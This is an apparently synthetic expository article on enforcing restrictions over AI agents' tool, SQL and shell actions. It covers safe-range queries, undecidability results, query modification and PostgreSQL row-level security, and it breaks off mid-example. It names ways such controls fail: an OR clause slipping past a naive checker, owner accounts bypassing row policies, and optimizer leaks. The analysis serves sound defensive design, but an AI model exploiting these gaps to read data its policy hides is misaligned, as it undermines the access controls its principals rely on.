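# Expressive Action Spaces and Enforceable Restrictions for AI Agents

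## What an action interface is and what it takes to restrict one

An AI agent's action interface is the set of requests the agent can make, including tool calls, queries, programs, commands and clicks on a screen. A wide interface lets an agent do many kinds of work, but it also makes rules harder to enforce. For example, it is hard to guarantee that an agent free to write any program will never delete a shared folder or read a colleague's private appointments. Database researchers have worked on this problem since the 1970s, when open-ended query languages for shared data first appeared. They have since proved which of these languages can be restricted without loss, which cannot, and how much computation the checking requires.

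### How a model's output becomes an action

A large language model (LLM) takes in text, and often images, and produces text, but it needs other software to act on that text. *From Question Answering to Task Completion* (Guo, Hao et al., 2026) describes an LLM agent as a model coupled to a "harness", the software that assembles the model's input, carries out actions, stores state and checks results. The model proposes a step, and the harness can run, reject or repair it.

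Anthropic's *How tool use works*, part of the developer documentation for its Claude models, describes how a model uses tools. A developer's program sends the model a message and a list of tools, each with a schema that describes its arguments. If the model's reply contains a tool request, the program reads the arguments, runs the operation and sends the result back as part of the conversation. This repeats until the model replies without requesting a tool. "The model never runs anything on its own," Anthropic writes. This applies to database lookups, shell commands and mouse movements. For a few tools, Anthropic's servers run the operation instead of the developer's program.

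To be guaranteed, a restriction must be enforced after the model proposes an action and before the action is executed. An instruction in the prompt, such as "do not open other people's events", only changes what the model is likely to propose, and a hostile web page that the agent reads may undo that change. A rule in the harness, the database or the operating system applies to the request itself, whatever led the model to produce it.

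### The ladder of interfaces

Tools range from a calculator to a full desktop environment (*Agentic Large Language Models*, 2026), and it helps to rank the common ones by how much an agent can express through them.

Fixed tool calls with typed arguments are among the narrowest action interfaces. The developer lists the operations, and the model can only choose one and supply its arguments. OpenAI's developer guide *Function calling* gives the example of a weather tool that takes a location, which can be any text, and a unit, which must be celsius or fahrenheit. Zhu and Cai (2026), in *From Language Models to World-Acting Systems*, regard such calls as the most legible interface an agent can have, because the service receiving the call can authenticate the caller, validate the arguments and record the request. They caution that a sequence of individually permitted calls can still produce a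 forbidden result.

A query language allows a wider range of actions. With SQL, the standard language of relational databases, an agent can write a query that the designer never thought of, though an ordinary query touches nothing outside the database. General code adds variables, loops and any libraries available on the machine. *Agentic Artificial Intelligence (AI)* (2026), a survey of agent architectures, lists "rich control flow and state" as a strength of code and sandboxing risk as a drawback. A sandbox is an environment, enforced by the operating system or network, that limits which files, processes and hosts a program can reach. A tool call can also contain code. One tool in OpenAI's guide takes arbitrary Python text as its only input, so the number of tools on a list is a poor measure of how much an agent can do.

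On a command line, the agent types commands to a shell such as bash. *Terminal Agents* (2026), a survey, calls the terminal a "particularly consequential" medium because one text channel gives access to files, processes, logs, remote machines and command-line tools. One setting of *An Empirical Study of Harness Design for Coding Agents* (2026) removed the ready-made file, search and web tools and left bash for general work. In strict computational terms, a shell and a Python interpreter are equally powerful, since each can usually start the other. The shell ranks higher here only because it tends to give the agent access to more.

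The widest interface is a screen with a mouse and keyboard, which works on almost any program a person could use, including old or proprietary software that has no other interface. But a click has almost no meaning of its own, because its effect depends on the window layout, the timing, and state that may not be visible. Zhu and Cai describe the choice between typed calls and the screen as a trade "between explicit semantics and interface coverage".

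The ladder ranks interfaces by reach, but greater reach does not always mean greater danger. *Securing Computer-Use Agents* (2026) points out that a click can confirm the deletion of an account. A shell command has more direct authority over files and networks, but it is often easier to audit. An agent can also have several kinds of interface. The one in *Qwen-UI-Agent Technical Report* (2026) can click, run bash commands, call outside services with structured arguments, and ask the user to confirm a payment. A rule that covers only some of these channels is weak, because the agent can reach the same result through one the rule leaves out. This is why Zhu and Cai want the same policy to apply to structured calls and to actions on the screen.

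Surveys of agent design now treat this as a standard tradeoff. Guo and colleagues call it "flexibility versus controllability", because low-level tools are general but hard to use robustly, while high-level tools are more reliable but may narrow the agent's behaviour too much. They write that more expressive actions need stronger permission control, sandboxing, rollback and auditing. *Agentic Artificial Intelligence (AI)* identifies "safety through restricted scope" as the main advantage of predefined calls. These descriptions give the direction of the tradeoff, but not how much generality a particular restriction removes. Working that out requires a definite rule and a definite language.

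### A calendar database, and enough SQL to query it

Zhang, Sheng and colleagues (2022), in *Blockaid*, a paper on controlling what web applications read from their databases, use a small calendar as their example. It has three tables:

```
Users(UId, Name)
Events(EId, Title, Duration)
Attendances(UId, EId, ConfirmedAt)
```

UId and EId are ID numbers for users and events. Each row of Attendances records that a user attends an event and when the user confirmed. The rule to enforce is that users may see only the events they attend.

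Suppose Ben is user 2. He attends event 5, "Budget review", which lasts 60 minutes. His colleagues Ada and Chloe (users 1 and 3) attend event 6, "Surprise party for Ben", which lasts 90. An SQL query names the columns it wants after SELECT and the table after FROM, and WHERE keeps only the rows that meet a condition:

```
SELECT Title
FROM Events
WHERE Duration > 60
```

This returns the title of the party, which Ben may not see. To ask about Ben's own events, a query has to combine two tables. JOIN pairs the rows of one table with the rows of another, and ON states which pairs belong together:

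```
SELECT e.Title
FROM Events e
JOIN Attendances a ON a.EId = e.EId
WHERE a.UId = 2
```

Here e and a are short names for the tables. The query matches each event with its attendance records, the last line keeps only Ben's, and the result is "Budget review".

### Restricting and policing

Now let Ben's agent want the first query, the one for events longer than an hour. An enforcer can do three things about it.

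The developer can make the request inexpressible by withholding SQL and offering one tool, `my_events()`, which takes no arguments; the harness fills in Ben's number. OpenAI's guide recommends this pattern to avoid giving the model unnecessary work. If the program already knows which order a customer means, the refund tool should have no field for an order number. As a side effect, the model cannot specify anybody else's order. The guide also describes how a developer can attach a grammar to a free-text tool, so that the model can produce only text of a given form. Such a grammar could admit SQL queries only if they contain the join and the condition on Ben's number in the right place.

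A second option is to rewrite the request. The agent can write any query, and the enforcer adds the join and the condition `a.UId = 2` before the query runs. The query then returns nothing, so the party stays hidden. Zhang and colleagues object to this method, called query modification, because it can mislead. The agent may tell Ben that no event on the calendar lasts more than an hour, when the query showed only that none of his events does. Rewriting works on programs too. *Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms* (Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider, 2006) gives the example of a file whose existence is secret. A rewriter can alter an untrusted program so that its directory listings omit the file, without changing the behavior of a program that would have ignored the file anyway.

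Last, the enforcer can check each request and refuse it if it violates the policy. Blockaid runs queries that comply with the policy unchanged and returns an error for any others. The agent can still use the whole query language and never receives a silently altered answer. But the checker has to determine what an arbitrary query would reveal, which takes far more work than reading a tool's name.

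Restricting means changing the interface so that the agent cannot express a forbidden action or cannot have it carried out. The argument-free tool restricts, and so does rewriting, since the forbidden version never runs. A sandbox also restricts, because an agent that tries to read a file outside it gets nothing back. Policing means leaving the interface expressive and judging each action when the agent requests it, either alone or together with the trace, which is the sequence of earlier requests and their answers. The distinction is not perfectly sharp, since an operating system also looks up a permission each time a program opens a file. But that lookup only compares a file name with a list, while policing requires interpreting the request.

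### Sound checks, false refusals and needed generality

A check is sound if it never allows what the policy forbids. A checker that allows any query containing the text `a.UId = 2` is unsound, because the agent can write `WHERE a.UId = 2 OR a.UId = 3` and read Chloe's events along with Ben's. A checker that accepts only the exact join query printed above is sound, but it blocks the same query with the condition written as `2 = a.UId`. Blocking an action that the policy allows is a false refusal.

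A strictly sound checker never wrongly allows an action. A checker that refuses everything meets this standard, so the difficulty is in being sound while blocking few harmless actions. Zhang and colleagues make soundness the basic requirement of Blockaid and accept that it may block some harmless queries, though it blocked none in their evaluation on three existing web applications. Other designers let both kinds of error vary. *Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents* (2026) tests monitors on the actions of command-line agents, counts wrongly allowed actions as security failures and wrongly blocked ones as lost utility, and plots the two against each other as the tolerated level of risk changes.

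How much a refusal matters depends on what the agent is for. Needed generality is the range of tasks that the agent's principal (the person or organisation it acts for) wants done. A calendar assistant loses no needed generality if it cannot compile software, but it probably loses some if it cannot tell Ben who else will be at the budget review.

An agent can lose generality it needs in two ways. First, the interface may have no way to express the task. If `my_events()` returns only titles and durations, no call can list the people at the budget review. A developer can often spot such a gap by reading the tool list, but closing it means adding a tool, which widens the interface. Second, the enforcer may refuse a task that the agent can express, as with `2 = a.UId`. These losses show up only in use and can depend on incidental details of wording. Sometimes the agent can get through by rephrasing.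 Otherwise, the checker needs to be improved, but the policy can stay the same.

### Why no checker judges every program correctly

No checker for general code can be both sound and free of false refusals, because the question it would have to answer is undecidable. This means that no single procedure answers it correctly, in finite time, for every program, though individual programs may be easy to judge. The classic example, from Alan Turing's work of 1936, is whether a given program will ever finish. If a checker could always tell, someone could write a program that runs the checker on its own text and does the opposite of the verdict, looping forever if the verdict is "finishes" and stopping if it is "runs forever". The checker would be wrong about that program. The same problem arises with forbidden actions. If we take any program, cut off its access to the calendar, and add a last line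 that deletes the calendar, the new program deletes the calendar exactly when the original finishes. A checker that was always right about deletion would therefore also be right about finishing. In his 1951 doctoral dissertation, Henry Gordon Rice proved more generally that every property of what programs do is undecidable if some programs have it and others lack it.

A real computer has finite memory, so an exhaustive search of its states would in principle settle the matter, but there are too many states to search in practice. The theorem also does not cover every question about programs. Hamlen and colleagues list some that a checker can always decide before the program runs, such as whether it stops within 100 steps. These questions do not include whether a program will ever write to the part of a disk from which the computer starts up.

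The impossibility applies only to checkers that are always right, and a sound checker can be wrong as long as it never admits a forbidden program. In *Program Analysis Is Harder Than Verification*, Cousot, Giacobazzi and Ranzato prove a version of Rice's theorem for tools that analyse or verify programs. Outside trivial cases, no such tool is both sound and complete, so a sound checker must refuse some acceptable programs. In an example from Hamlen and colleagues, a checker guarantees that programs finish by admitting only those that finish within 100 steps, but it also refuses every program that would have finished later. A monitor that runs alongside the program can instead step in just before a forbidden write, without predicting the whole run, although monitors have limits of their own.

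A false refusal does little harm if the agent can do the same work with a different expression. Ideally, the restriction is an effective syntax, a rule a computer can check that admits only acceptable expressions and at least one for every acceptable behaviour. Rice's theorem does not rule this out. For example, if the policy forbids deleting the calendar, the developer can remove the delete operation from the programming language. This also excludes programs that contain the operation but never reach it, but each has an equivalent without the operation, so the agent keeps all of its permitted behaviour.

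## Safe queries in the relational calculus

The relational calculus is a query language made of logical formulas. Some formulas have infinite answers, which no database system can return, and no algorithm can always tell whether a given formula is one of them. But a short list of rules about the form of a query excludes all such formulas and still leaves at least one way to write every usable query. The calculus therefore has an effective syntax.

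### Formulas as queries

Edgar Codd, a researcher at IBM, developed the relational calculus in the early 1970s to state what data a person wants without stating how to find it. The simplest formulas are table lookups such as `Users(u, n)`, which is true if the `Users` table has a row with those values. Larger formulas combine lookups and equalities with ∧ (and), ∨ (or), ¬ (not) and ∃x (there is some x). ∀x (for every x) is shorthand for ¬∃x¬. A variable is free if no ∃ or ∀ introduces it, and the answer to a query consists of all values of the free variables that make the formula true.

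The following formula returns the people in the calendar database who attend event 5, the budget review. The variable c is the time the person confirmed.

```
∃c. Attendances(u, 5, c)
```

Suppose that Ben, Ada and Chloe are the only users and that only Ben attends. The answer is then Ben's number, 2. A ¬ in front asks for everyone who does not attend:

```
¬ ∃c. Attendances(u, 5, c)
```

Most people would expect the answer to be Ada and Chloe, numbers 1 and 3. But nothing in the formula requires u to be a user. The number 99 makes it true, and so does the text "Budget review", because neither is the number of somebody attending event 5. With infinitely many possible numbers and texts, the answer is infinite. The remedy is to ask for users who do not attend:

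```
(∃n. Users(u, n)) ∧ ¬ ∃c. Attendances(u, 5, c)
```

The answer is now 1 and 3.

The domain is the set of values that variables may take. A query is domain independent if its answer depends only on the tables and on the constants in the query. The query with the Users lookup is domain independent, but the bare negation is not, because adding 99 to the domain also adds it to the answer, even though no table has changed. A domain-independent query always has a finite answer, because every value in the answer comes from a finite table or from the query itself.

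No algorithm can decide whether an arbitrary formula is domain independent, as Raszyk, Basin and colleagues (2022) note in *Efficient Evaluation of Arbitrary Relational Calculus Queries*. This follows from a theorem Boris Trakhtenbrot proved around 1950, which states that no algorithm can decide whether a logical sentence is true in some finite model, which here means on some database. According to *What reasonable first-order queries are permitted by Trakhtenbrot's theorem?*, this holds even for sentences about a single two-column relation. Suppose we use ∧ to join a domain-independent yes-or-no query F to the bare negation. If F is false on every database, the combined query always returns nothing, so it is domain independent. If F is true on even one database, the combined query has an infinite answer there, so it is not domain independent. A test for domain independence would therefore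 decide whether F is true on some database, which Trakhtenbrot's theorem rules out.

### The safe-range rules

The safe-range rules replace this question about meaning with a question about form. They determine which variables a formula limits, in the sense that its form forces their values to come from the tables or from the query's own constants. Textbooks call such variables range-restricted. In the version that Raszyk and colleagues use, the rules work as follows:

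- A table lookup limits every variable in it, so `Users(u, n)` limits u and n. An equality with a constant, such as e = 5, limits e.
- Two formulas joined by ∧ limit a variable if either of them does. An equality between variables passes the limit on: if one formula limits x and the other is x = y, together they also limit y.
- Two formulas joined by ∨ limit a variable only if both do. `Users(u, n) ∨ Events(e, t, d)` limits none of its variables, because as soon as the calendar has one event, any values of u and n make the formula true.
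- Putting ∃y in front of a formula leaves the limits on its other variables as they were.
- A negated lookup, or a negated ∃, limits nothing. Before giving up on a negation, however, the rules move it inward. Two negations cancel, a negated ∨ turns into an ∧ of negations, and a negated ∧ turns into an ∨ of negations.

A query is safe-range if it limits every free variable and if, wherever ∃y occurs, the formula after it limits y.

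In the query for users who do not attend event 5, the free variable is u. The Users lookup limits u and n, and the ∧ extends the limit on u to the whole query. The Attendances lookup limits c, the only variable the second ∃ needs limited, so the query passes. In the bare negation, the ¬ stands directly before an ∃, so nothing limits u and the query fails. A checker can decide both cases from the text of the query alone, without the data.

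The rules are sound, since every safe-range query is domain independent, but they also refuse some domain-independent formulas. Raszyk and colleagues give an example about a shop with three tables: B lists brands, P(b, p) records that brand b sells product p, and S(p, u, s) records that user u gave product p the score s. A brand is suspicious if some user gave all of its products the same score:

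```
B(b) ∧ ∃u,s. ∀p. P(b,p) → S(p,u,s)
```

The arrow means "if … then". The query closely follows the description in words, and it is domain independent because its answer contains only brands from B. But when ∀ and the arrow are rewritten using ∃ and negation, the part after ∃u,s begins with a negated ∃, which limits neither u nor s, so the checker refuses the query. An acceptable version must take u and s from the pairs of users and scores in S, and add the brands that have no products, for which the condition is trivially true. Raszyk and colleagues think that only the best students in an undergraduate database course would find the corresponding expression in relational algebra. A query refused in this way can still be expressed in an acceptable form, but someone has to rephrase it.

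### Why the rules lose no query

A mechanical method turns any domain-independent formula into an equivalent safe-range one. The first step is to write a formula AD(x) stating that x occurs somewhere in the tables or as a constant in the query. For the calendar, this is a long ∨ with one part for each column. The second step is to attach AD(x) with ∧ for each free variable x and wherever the query introduces a variable x. The result is safe-range because AD(x) limits x. It gives the same answer as the original evaluated on only the stored values and the query's constants. Because the original is domain independent, shrinking the domain in this way does not change the answer.

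*Queries with External Predicates* (Guagliardo, Libkin and colleagues, 2025) states the result in terms of finiteness: every formula whose answer is finite on all databases has a safe-range equivalent. This assumes an infinite domain and a query that uses only stored tables, with no arithmetic or other outside functions.

This is compatible with the undecidability of domain independence. No algorithm can decide for every formula whether it is domain independent, but a checker for safe-range form only has to accept one formula for each domain-independent query. The mechanical method also works on a formula that is not domain independent, but then it changes the meaning. The bare negation becomes a request for everything stored in the calendar, including event titles and durations, except the numbers of people attending event 5. No algorithm can always tell whether the rewriting has changed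 the meaning.

A more elaborate checker can reject fewer good expressions. Guagliardo and colleagues also track which variables a formula's negation would limit, and their system accepts some formulas that the safe-range rules reject. Whether it accepts an expression still depends on how the expression is written. For example, the rows common to two tables A and B can be written as A − (A − B), or by pairing the rows of A with those of B and keeping the matches. When A or B is an outside function, the system can derive guarantees for the second form that it cannot derive for the first.

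### Codd's theorem and SQL

Relational algebra describes queries as operations on finite tables. It can pick rows, keep certain columns, combine tables, and subtract one table from another. By Codd's theorem (1972), the algebra can express every domain-independent query of the calculus. To find the people not attending event 5, a query takes the column of user numbers from Users and subtracts the numbers of those who attend. The bare negation has no counterpart in the algebra, because subtraction needs a table to subtract from.

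SQL took the algebra as its foundation and inherited this limitation. In an SQL query, each variable stands for a row of a table named after FROM:

```
SELECT u.UId
FROM Users u
WHERE NOT EXISTS (
  SELECT * FROM Attendances a
  WHERE a.UId = u.UId AND a.EId = 5)
```

People who write SQL therefore work under a safety restriction that most of them never notice.

Negation in SQL has a pitfall that the basic calculus lacks, because SQL allows missing values. It marks them as NULL, and comparing anything with NULL gives "unknown" rather than true or false. Suppose the Attendances table had a row for event 5 with no user number, and the query used `NOT IN` instead of `NOT EXISTS`. SQL could not establish that Ada's or Chloe's number differs from the missing one, so the query would return nobody. In *Relational Algebra and Calculus with SQL Null Values*, Franconi and Tessaris (2022) extended Codd's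 theorem to cover this behaviour, proving that an algebra with SQL's nulls has the same power as the domain-independent part of a suitably adapted logic. The restricted language therefore still matches the queries people need, provided that the logic treats missing values as SQL does.

### Answering any formula whose answer is finite

Some useful queries have finite answers on most databases even though they are not domain independent. In the shop example, an analyst may want to find the users whose scores made a brand suspicious. In the calculus, this only requires removing u from the ∃, which makes u free. The answer is finite if every brand has a product, but if some brand has none, every value of u meets the condition and the answer is infinite. The algebra cannot express this query, and no safe-range formula is equivalent to it.

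Raszyk and colleagues devised a translation that handles such queries. It assumes an infinite domain and turns any calculus query into two safe-range queries. The first returns yes exactly when the original query has an infinite answer on the current database. If it returns no, the second computes the original query's answer. In the example of finding the users behind suspicious brands, the first query checks whether any brand in B has no product in P.

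The translation handles one unlimited variable at a time. A value of such a variable x may appear in the relevant table columns or equal another variable that the query compares with x. If it does neither, it is "fresh". Every lookup that contains x is false for a fresh value, so the translator replaces those lookups with "false" and simplifies the formula. If the result is true for some values of the other variables, infinitely many fresh values of x satisfy the query and the answer is infinite. Otherwise, the translator can limit x to the first two cases. In the bare negation, replacing the Attendances lookup leaves "not false", which is true, so the answer is infinite on every calendar. In the corrected query, the Users lookup also becomes false, which makes the whole formula false, so the answer is always finite.

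This is policing instead of restricting, and the check accepts a query exactly when its answer is finite. An exact check is possible because it concerns a single database, whereas domain independence is undecidable because it concerns all possible databases.

Raszyk and colleagues proved the translation correct in Isabelle/HOL, a program that checks mathematical proofs. While doing so, they found an error in the version they had presented at a conference. One step could combine equalities in a way that produced a query outside the safe-range form, though later steps in their software happened to compensate for this.

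Their program, RC2SQL, converts both safe-range queries into SQL and runs them on an ordinary database system. They compared it with several other methods, including an older translation by Allen Van Gelder and Rodney Topor, which they reimplemented because they found no public version. The older method draws users and scores separately and may have to consider every combination, while RC2SQL draws only the pairs that occur in the reviews. If n products each have reviews from m users, and no two users ever give the same score, the older method needs time proportional to at least n·m² and RC2SQL roughly n·m.

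RC2SQL with the PostgreSQL database system took between 0.5 and 2.2 seconds on ten randomly generated queries over medium-sized artificial databases, while the older translation exceeded the 300-second limit on four of them. At the largest size, RC2SQL took 2.8 to 14.1 seconds. In another experiment, on five queries that could have infinite answers, it recognised each infinite case in about half a second. Other tests used real Amazon reviews, 147,194 of gift cards and about 1.5 million of musical instruments. Both translations ran on PostgreSQL in the tests below.

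| Query | Gift cards, RC2SQL | Gift cards, older translation | Instruments, RC2SQL | Instruments, older translation |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Suspicious brands | 1.6 s | 1.9 s | 8.4 s | 10.0 s |
| Users behind suspicious brands | 2.5 s | not applicable | 11.9 s | not applicable |
| Suspicious brands, by same score or same review text | 4.9 s | over 300 s | 51.3 s | over 300 s |

The extra generality adds little running time here, but only with an optimisation that compares counts instead of building large combined tables. Without it, RC2SQL took 133 seconds to find suspicious brands in the gift card data and timed out on the musical instruments data.

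### Where no effective syntax exists

The calculus described so far can only look values up and compare them for equality, but real queries usually do more. Guagliardo and colleagues point out that none of the queries in TPC-H and TPC-DS, two standard database benchmarks, is pure relational algebra. Once a language includes functions such as addition, whether an answer is finite can depend on what the functions do. For example, a query for all pairs of whole numbers that add up to 60, the length of the budget review in minutes, has infinitely many answers if negative numbers are allowed and 61 if they are not. SQL avoids the problem by computing a function only when its inputs are given, so a query can add two stored numbers but cannot ask for all pairs with a given sum. Some newer languages, such as Rel, allow both kinds of query.

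With built-in functions and relations, an effective syntax may not exist. *Finite Queries do not Have Effective Syntax* (Stolboushkin and Taitslin, 1995) proves that for some domains, no computable set of formulas contains at least one version of every query with finite answers and nothing else. *On problems of databases over a fixed infinite universe* (Belegradek, Stolboushkin and Taitslin, 1999) describes such a domain in which a computer can evaluate the built-in operations and an algorithm can decide every logical statement about them. In that domain, no algorithm can decide whether a query's answer is finite on a given database, so an exact check at the time of the request is also impossible.

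Guagliardo and colleagues explain why this negative result is consistent with a positive result of their own. Suppose a system can only test whether given values satisfy an outside function. Then, if a single algorithm can compute a query no matter what the function does, their rules accept an equivalent query. The negative result concerns queries that are finite for one particular choice of functions but may be infinite for others.

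A different kind of failure affects programs that always halt. Suppose that a programming language contains only programs that halt on every input, and that a computer can check whether a text is a program in it. The computer can then list all programs that take and return a whole number as P₀, P₁, P₂ and so on. Define a new computation D that, given a number n, runs the program Pₙ on the input n and adds 1 to the result:

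```
D(n) = Pₙ(n) + 1
```

D always halts, because each Pₙ does. If the language contained a program for D, that program would be Pₖ for some k. But D returns Pₖ(k) + 1 on input k, which differs from what Pₖ returns, so the language has no program for D. Adding D produces a larger language, to which the same argument applies. Therefore, no language of always-halting programs can express every always-halting computation.

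This argument does not apply to the calculus, because the calculus cannot run its own queries from a numbered list. The counterpart of D is therefore not a calculus query, and an effective syntax for calculus queries does not have to include it. For programs, D is one of the always-halting computations the syntax was supposed to cover. Losing D may still matter little in practice, because D amounts to an interpreter for the restricted language, and a calendar assistant has little need for one.

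Recursion, in which a query refers to its own results, can also end the guarantee. A calculus query can find everyone who shares an event with Ben, everyone who shares an event with one of those people, and so on for any fixed number of steps, but it cannot find everyone connected to Ben by a chain of any length. Datalog, a rule-based query language, can express that query because it allows recursion. Stolboushkin and Taitslin (1998), in *Safe Stratified Datalog with Integer Order Does Not Have Syntax*, proved that safe programs have no effective syntax in a version of Datalog that also has negation and the ordering of the integers.

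Other properties are hard to make decidable by changing the syntax, even in the plain calculus. One is whether a yes-or-no query can ever be true. *An Extension of Trakhtenbrot's Theorem* (2021) proves that this property is undecidable in any computable part of the logic that keeps the logic's full power over finite databases and lets a computer combine any two sentences with "and". This matters for access control because whether a query could ever reveal a private row is a question of the same type.

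### What a safe query can still do

In this theory, "safe" means only that the answer is finite. A safe query can still take longer than anyone could wait. In a company with 1,000 users, a query that lists every sequence of ten users, with repeats allowed, returns 10³⁰ rows. A finite answer can also do harm. For example, a burglar could use a list of everyone at a weekend retreat to find empty homes.

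The safe-range rules also do not depend on who is asking. The query for events longer than an hour satisfies all of them, and on the calendar it returns the title "Surprise party for Ben" to both Ada and Ben.

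## Query modification and row-level security

Query modification adds conditions to each query so that it reaches only rows the user may see. An agent can use all of SQL, and the system refuses none of its queries. However, some answers are wrong, and nothing marks them as wrong.

### From INGRES to rules for agents

Stonebraker and Wong (1974), in *Access Control in a Relational Data Base Management System by Query Modification*, described query modification for INGRES, an early relational system they were building at Berkeley. In their example, an employee named Smith may see only his own row of the employee table but requests Jones's salary. INGRES keeps the condition in his query, that the name is Jones, and adds the condition from his permission, that the name is Smith. No row meets both conditions, so the answer is empty.

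A permission in INGRES consists of a list of columns and a condition on rows. For each table variable in a query, INGRES collects the columns the query uses and finds the user's permissions that cover all of them. It connects the conditions of those permissions with "or" and attaches the result to the query with "and". It then processes the query like any other. Stonebraker and Wong expected the overhead to be negligible in most cases and pointed out that an added condition can speed up a query by letting the system use an index.

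Oracle later built the idea into its database as a feature called Virtual Private Database. An administrator attaches a policy function to a table (Byun, 2004, *Access Control by Query Modification*). When a user queries the table, Oracle calls the function and adds the condition it returns, such as `owner = USER`, to the query. Because the function is a program, it can return different conditions for different users and none for an administrator.

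PostgreSQL, a widely used open-source system, has a version known as row-level security. To enforce the rule that users see only the events they attend, an administrator switches row security on for the Events table and writes a policy:

```
CREATE POLICY own_events ON Events
FOR SELECT
USING (EId IN (SELECT EId FROM Attendances
               WHERE UId = my_user_id()))
```

Here `my_user_id()` is a function supplied by the administrator that returns the current user's number. Suppose that Ben's agent looks for events of an hour or longer:

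```
SELECT Title FROM Events
WHERE Duration >= 60
```

In effect, PostgreSQL runs this query instead:

```
SELECT Title FROM Events
WHERE Duration >= 60
  AND EId IN (SELECT EId FROM Attendances
              WHERE UId = 2)
```

The original would return "Budget review" and "Surprise party for Ben". The modified query returns only "Budget review".

If an administrator enables row security but writes no policy, no rows are visible, according to PostgreSQL's documentation. But a table's owner usually bypasses its policies, so an agent that connects under the owner's account does too. *CREATE POLICY*, Arch Linux's copy of the PostgreSQL manual page, states that hidden rows are normally left out of a result without an error, while an attempt to store a row that violates the policy causes one.

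Query modification is attractive because it restricts the user so little. An agent limited to the `my_events()` tool can only fetch a list, but an agent querying under row-level security can sort, group and join Ben's events in ways no developer planned for. The developer also does not have to repeat the access rule in every program that uses the calendar.

Database vendors now recommend this approach for AI agents. Oracle (2026), in a technical brief on its Deep Data Security product, advises customers to treat everything a model reads or writes as untrusted and to constrain access "by policy, not model behavior". Agents write SQL as they go and often run it through accounts with broad privileges, so they bypass checks in application code. Oracle considers confining agents to predefined functions a poor alternative because it makes them less useful for analysis and unplanned questions.

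In Oracle's design, the agent's connection passes the end user's identity to the database with every statement, and the database rewrites the statement according to rules called data grants. These rules can cover rows, columns or single cells. For example, they can let a manager update the salaries of direct reports but not the manager's own. *Fine Grained Authorization Through Predicated Grants*, by Chaudhuri, Dutta and Sudarshan, had earlier proposed attaching such conditions to SQL's ordinary permissions. Oracle's brief is product documentation and contains no tests against attacks, but the database adds Ben's condition even if a hostile web page causes his agent to request every event.

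### Wrong answers without a warning

Suppose the calendar holds three events, which last 30, 60 and 240 minutes, and Ben attends the first two. His agent wants the average length of all events:

```
SELECT AVG(Duration) FROM Events
```

The correct answer is 110. The modified query averages only the events Ben attends and returns 45, with no sign that anything is missing. That result is right if Ben wants to know how long his own meetings last, but it is less than half the true figure if he is working out how long the company's meeting rooms are in use. The error also has no upper limit, because the query would still return 45 if the hidden event lasted a week.

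Stonebraker and Wong already knew of this problem. In their example, Adams may see salaries only for the toy department. When he asks for the company's average salary, he gets the toy department's average, which they say is "probably not what he wants". They let administrators exempt averages over a whole table from modification, but this made two equivalent queries give different answers. `AVE(X.SALARY)` returned the true company average, while the same query with a condition that every employee meets, such as having a name later in the alphabet than "AAAAA", returned the toy department's average.

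Even without averages, the answer can depend on the wording of the query. In another of their examples, Jones may see names, managers and salaries only for employees who earn more than their managers. If his query finds those employees by comparing two copies of the table, INGRES adds the condition to both copies, and he gets only the employees whose managers also earn more than their own managers. If he just asks for names and salaries, INGRES adds the condition once, and he gets all the employees who earn more than their managers.

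Negation causes a different error. Suppose a similar rule hides the attendance records of events that Ben does not attend, and his agent asks which users are not going to event 6, the surprise party. Ada and Chloe are going, but their records are hidden, so the query returns all three users, and two of those rows are false.

A query is monotonic if adding rows to the tables never removes a row from its answer. Hiding rows from such a query can shorten the answer but cannot put anything false into it. The query for events of an hour or longer is monotonic, but the query for people who are not going to the party isn't, because a new attendance record can remove a person from the answer.

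Byun's slides call this whole approach the "Truman model" and contrast it with a "non-Truman" model, which runs a query unchanged or rejects it.

### Three criteria for a correct answer

Wang, Yu and colleagues (2007), in *On the Correctness Criteria of Fine-Grained Access Control in Relational Databases*, defined what a system that hides data should achieve. Let D be the database, P the policy and Q the query. S(D, Q) is the ordinary answer without access control, and A(D, P, Q) is the answer the system gives, in which it may mark some cells "unauthorized". The three criteria are as follows:

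- **Sound:** the answer contains nothing false. Every row of A(D, P, Q) matches a row of S(D, Q), except in cells marked "unauthorized".
- **Secure:** the answer depends only on permitted information. If D and D′ differ only in what P hides, then A(D, P, Q) = A(D′, P, Q).
- **Maximum:** the answer contains at least as much as any other answer that would be free of falsehoods on every database that differs from D only in what P hides.

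The word "sound" has a different meaning here than it has for checkers, where it is closer to what Wang and colleagues call secure.

By these criteria, Ben's average of 45 is secure, because changing the hidden event's length would not change it. But it is not sound, because the true answer is 110. The true average depends on the hidden event, so the best answer that meets all three criteria is a single cell marked "unauthorized", which amounts to a refusal.

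The third criterion is needed because a system that always returns nothing is both sound and secure. Wang and colleagues also proved that security for single queries extends to sequences of queries and to groups of users who pool their answers. If each answer is the same on D and D′, so is anything computed from the answers. An agent that sends thousands of queries therefore learns no more than the policy allows, provided the data doesn't change in the meantime.

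Wang and colleagues found that existing systems were not sound. One method replaced each hidden cell with NULL and then ran the query as usual. In their example, a customer table includes Jack, who is 21, and Nick, who is 34 but whose age is hidden. A query takes all customers and subtracts those aged 25 or over, which should leave only Jack. Because a comparison with NULL is never true, the query does not subtract Nick and wrongly includes him in the answer. They observed similar problems in experiments with Oracle's column-level Virtual Private Database.

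Their own method evaluates each part of a query in two ways, to find the rows that certainly belong to the result and all the rows that could belong to it, given the hidden values. To subtract a second group of rows from a first, the method takes the certain members of the first and removes every possible member of the second. Nick could be 25 or over, so the method removes him, and only Jack remains. Wang and colleagues proved that the method is sound and secure, and implemented it by rewriting queries for an existing database system. Its rules cover the operations of relational algebra, which do not include averages or counts.

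The method is not maximum, because it can leave out rows that it could safely return. Suppose a query asks for customers who are either over 29 or at most 29. Nick matches whatever his age, so including him would reveal nothing about it, but the method leaves him out because it treats his age as unknown. To include him, it would have to detect that the condition is always true. No algorithm can do this in every case if conditions can contain multiplication of whole numbers.

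Oracle's 2026 design also returns NULL for hidden cells by default. SQL's AVG ignores NULLs, so a rule that hid the length of the 240-minute event but left its row visible would produce 45 again. Oracle offers two partial remedies. The first is a set of SQL functions that distinguish hidden values from missing ones, so an agent that checks can tell that its average is incomplete. The second is to let trusted code briefly receive greater privileges and return a total without the records behind it. In the calendar example, a tool could return the company-wide average of 110 this way. But as with any fixed tool, a developer has to foresee the question and decide that the result is safe to release.

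### Leaks inside a rewritten query

Even a correctly rewritten query can reveal hidden rows while it runs. A query's conditions define which rows belong in the answer, but the database's optimizer, the component that plans how to run the query, may choose the order in which to test them. If it tests the user's own condition first, that condition sees rows the policy is about to remove. Suppose Ben's agent sends this query:

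```
SELECT Title FROM Events
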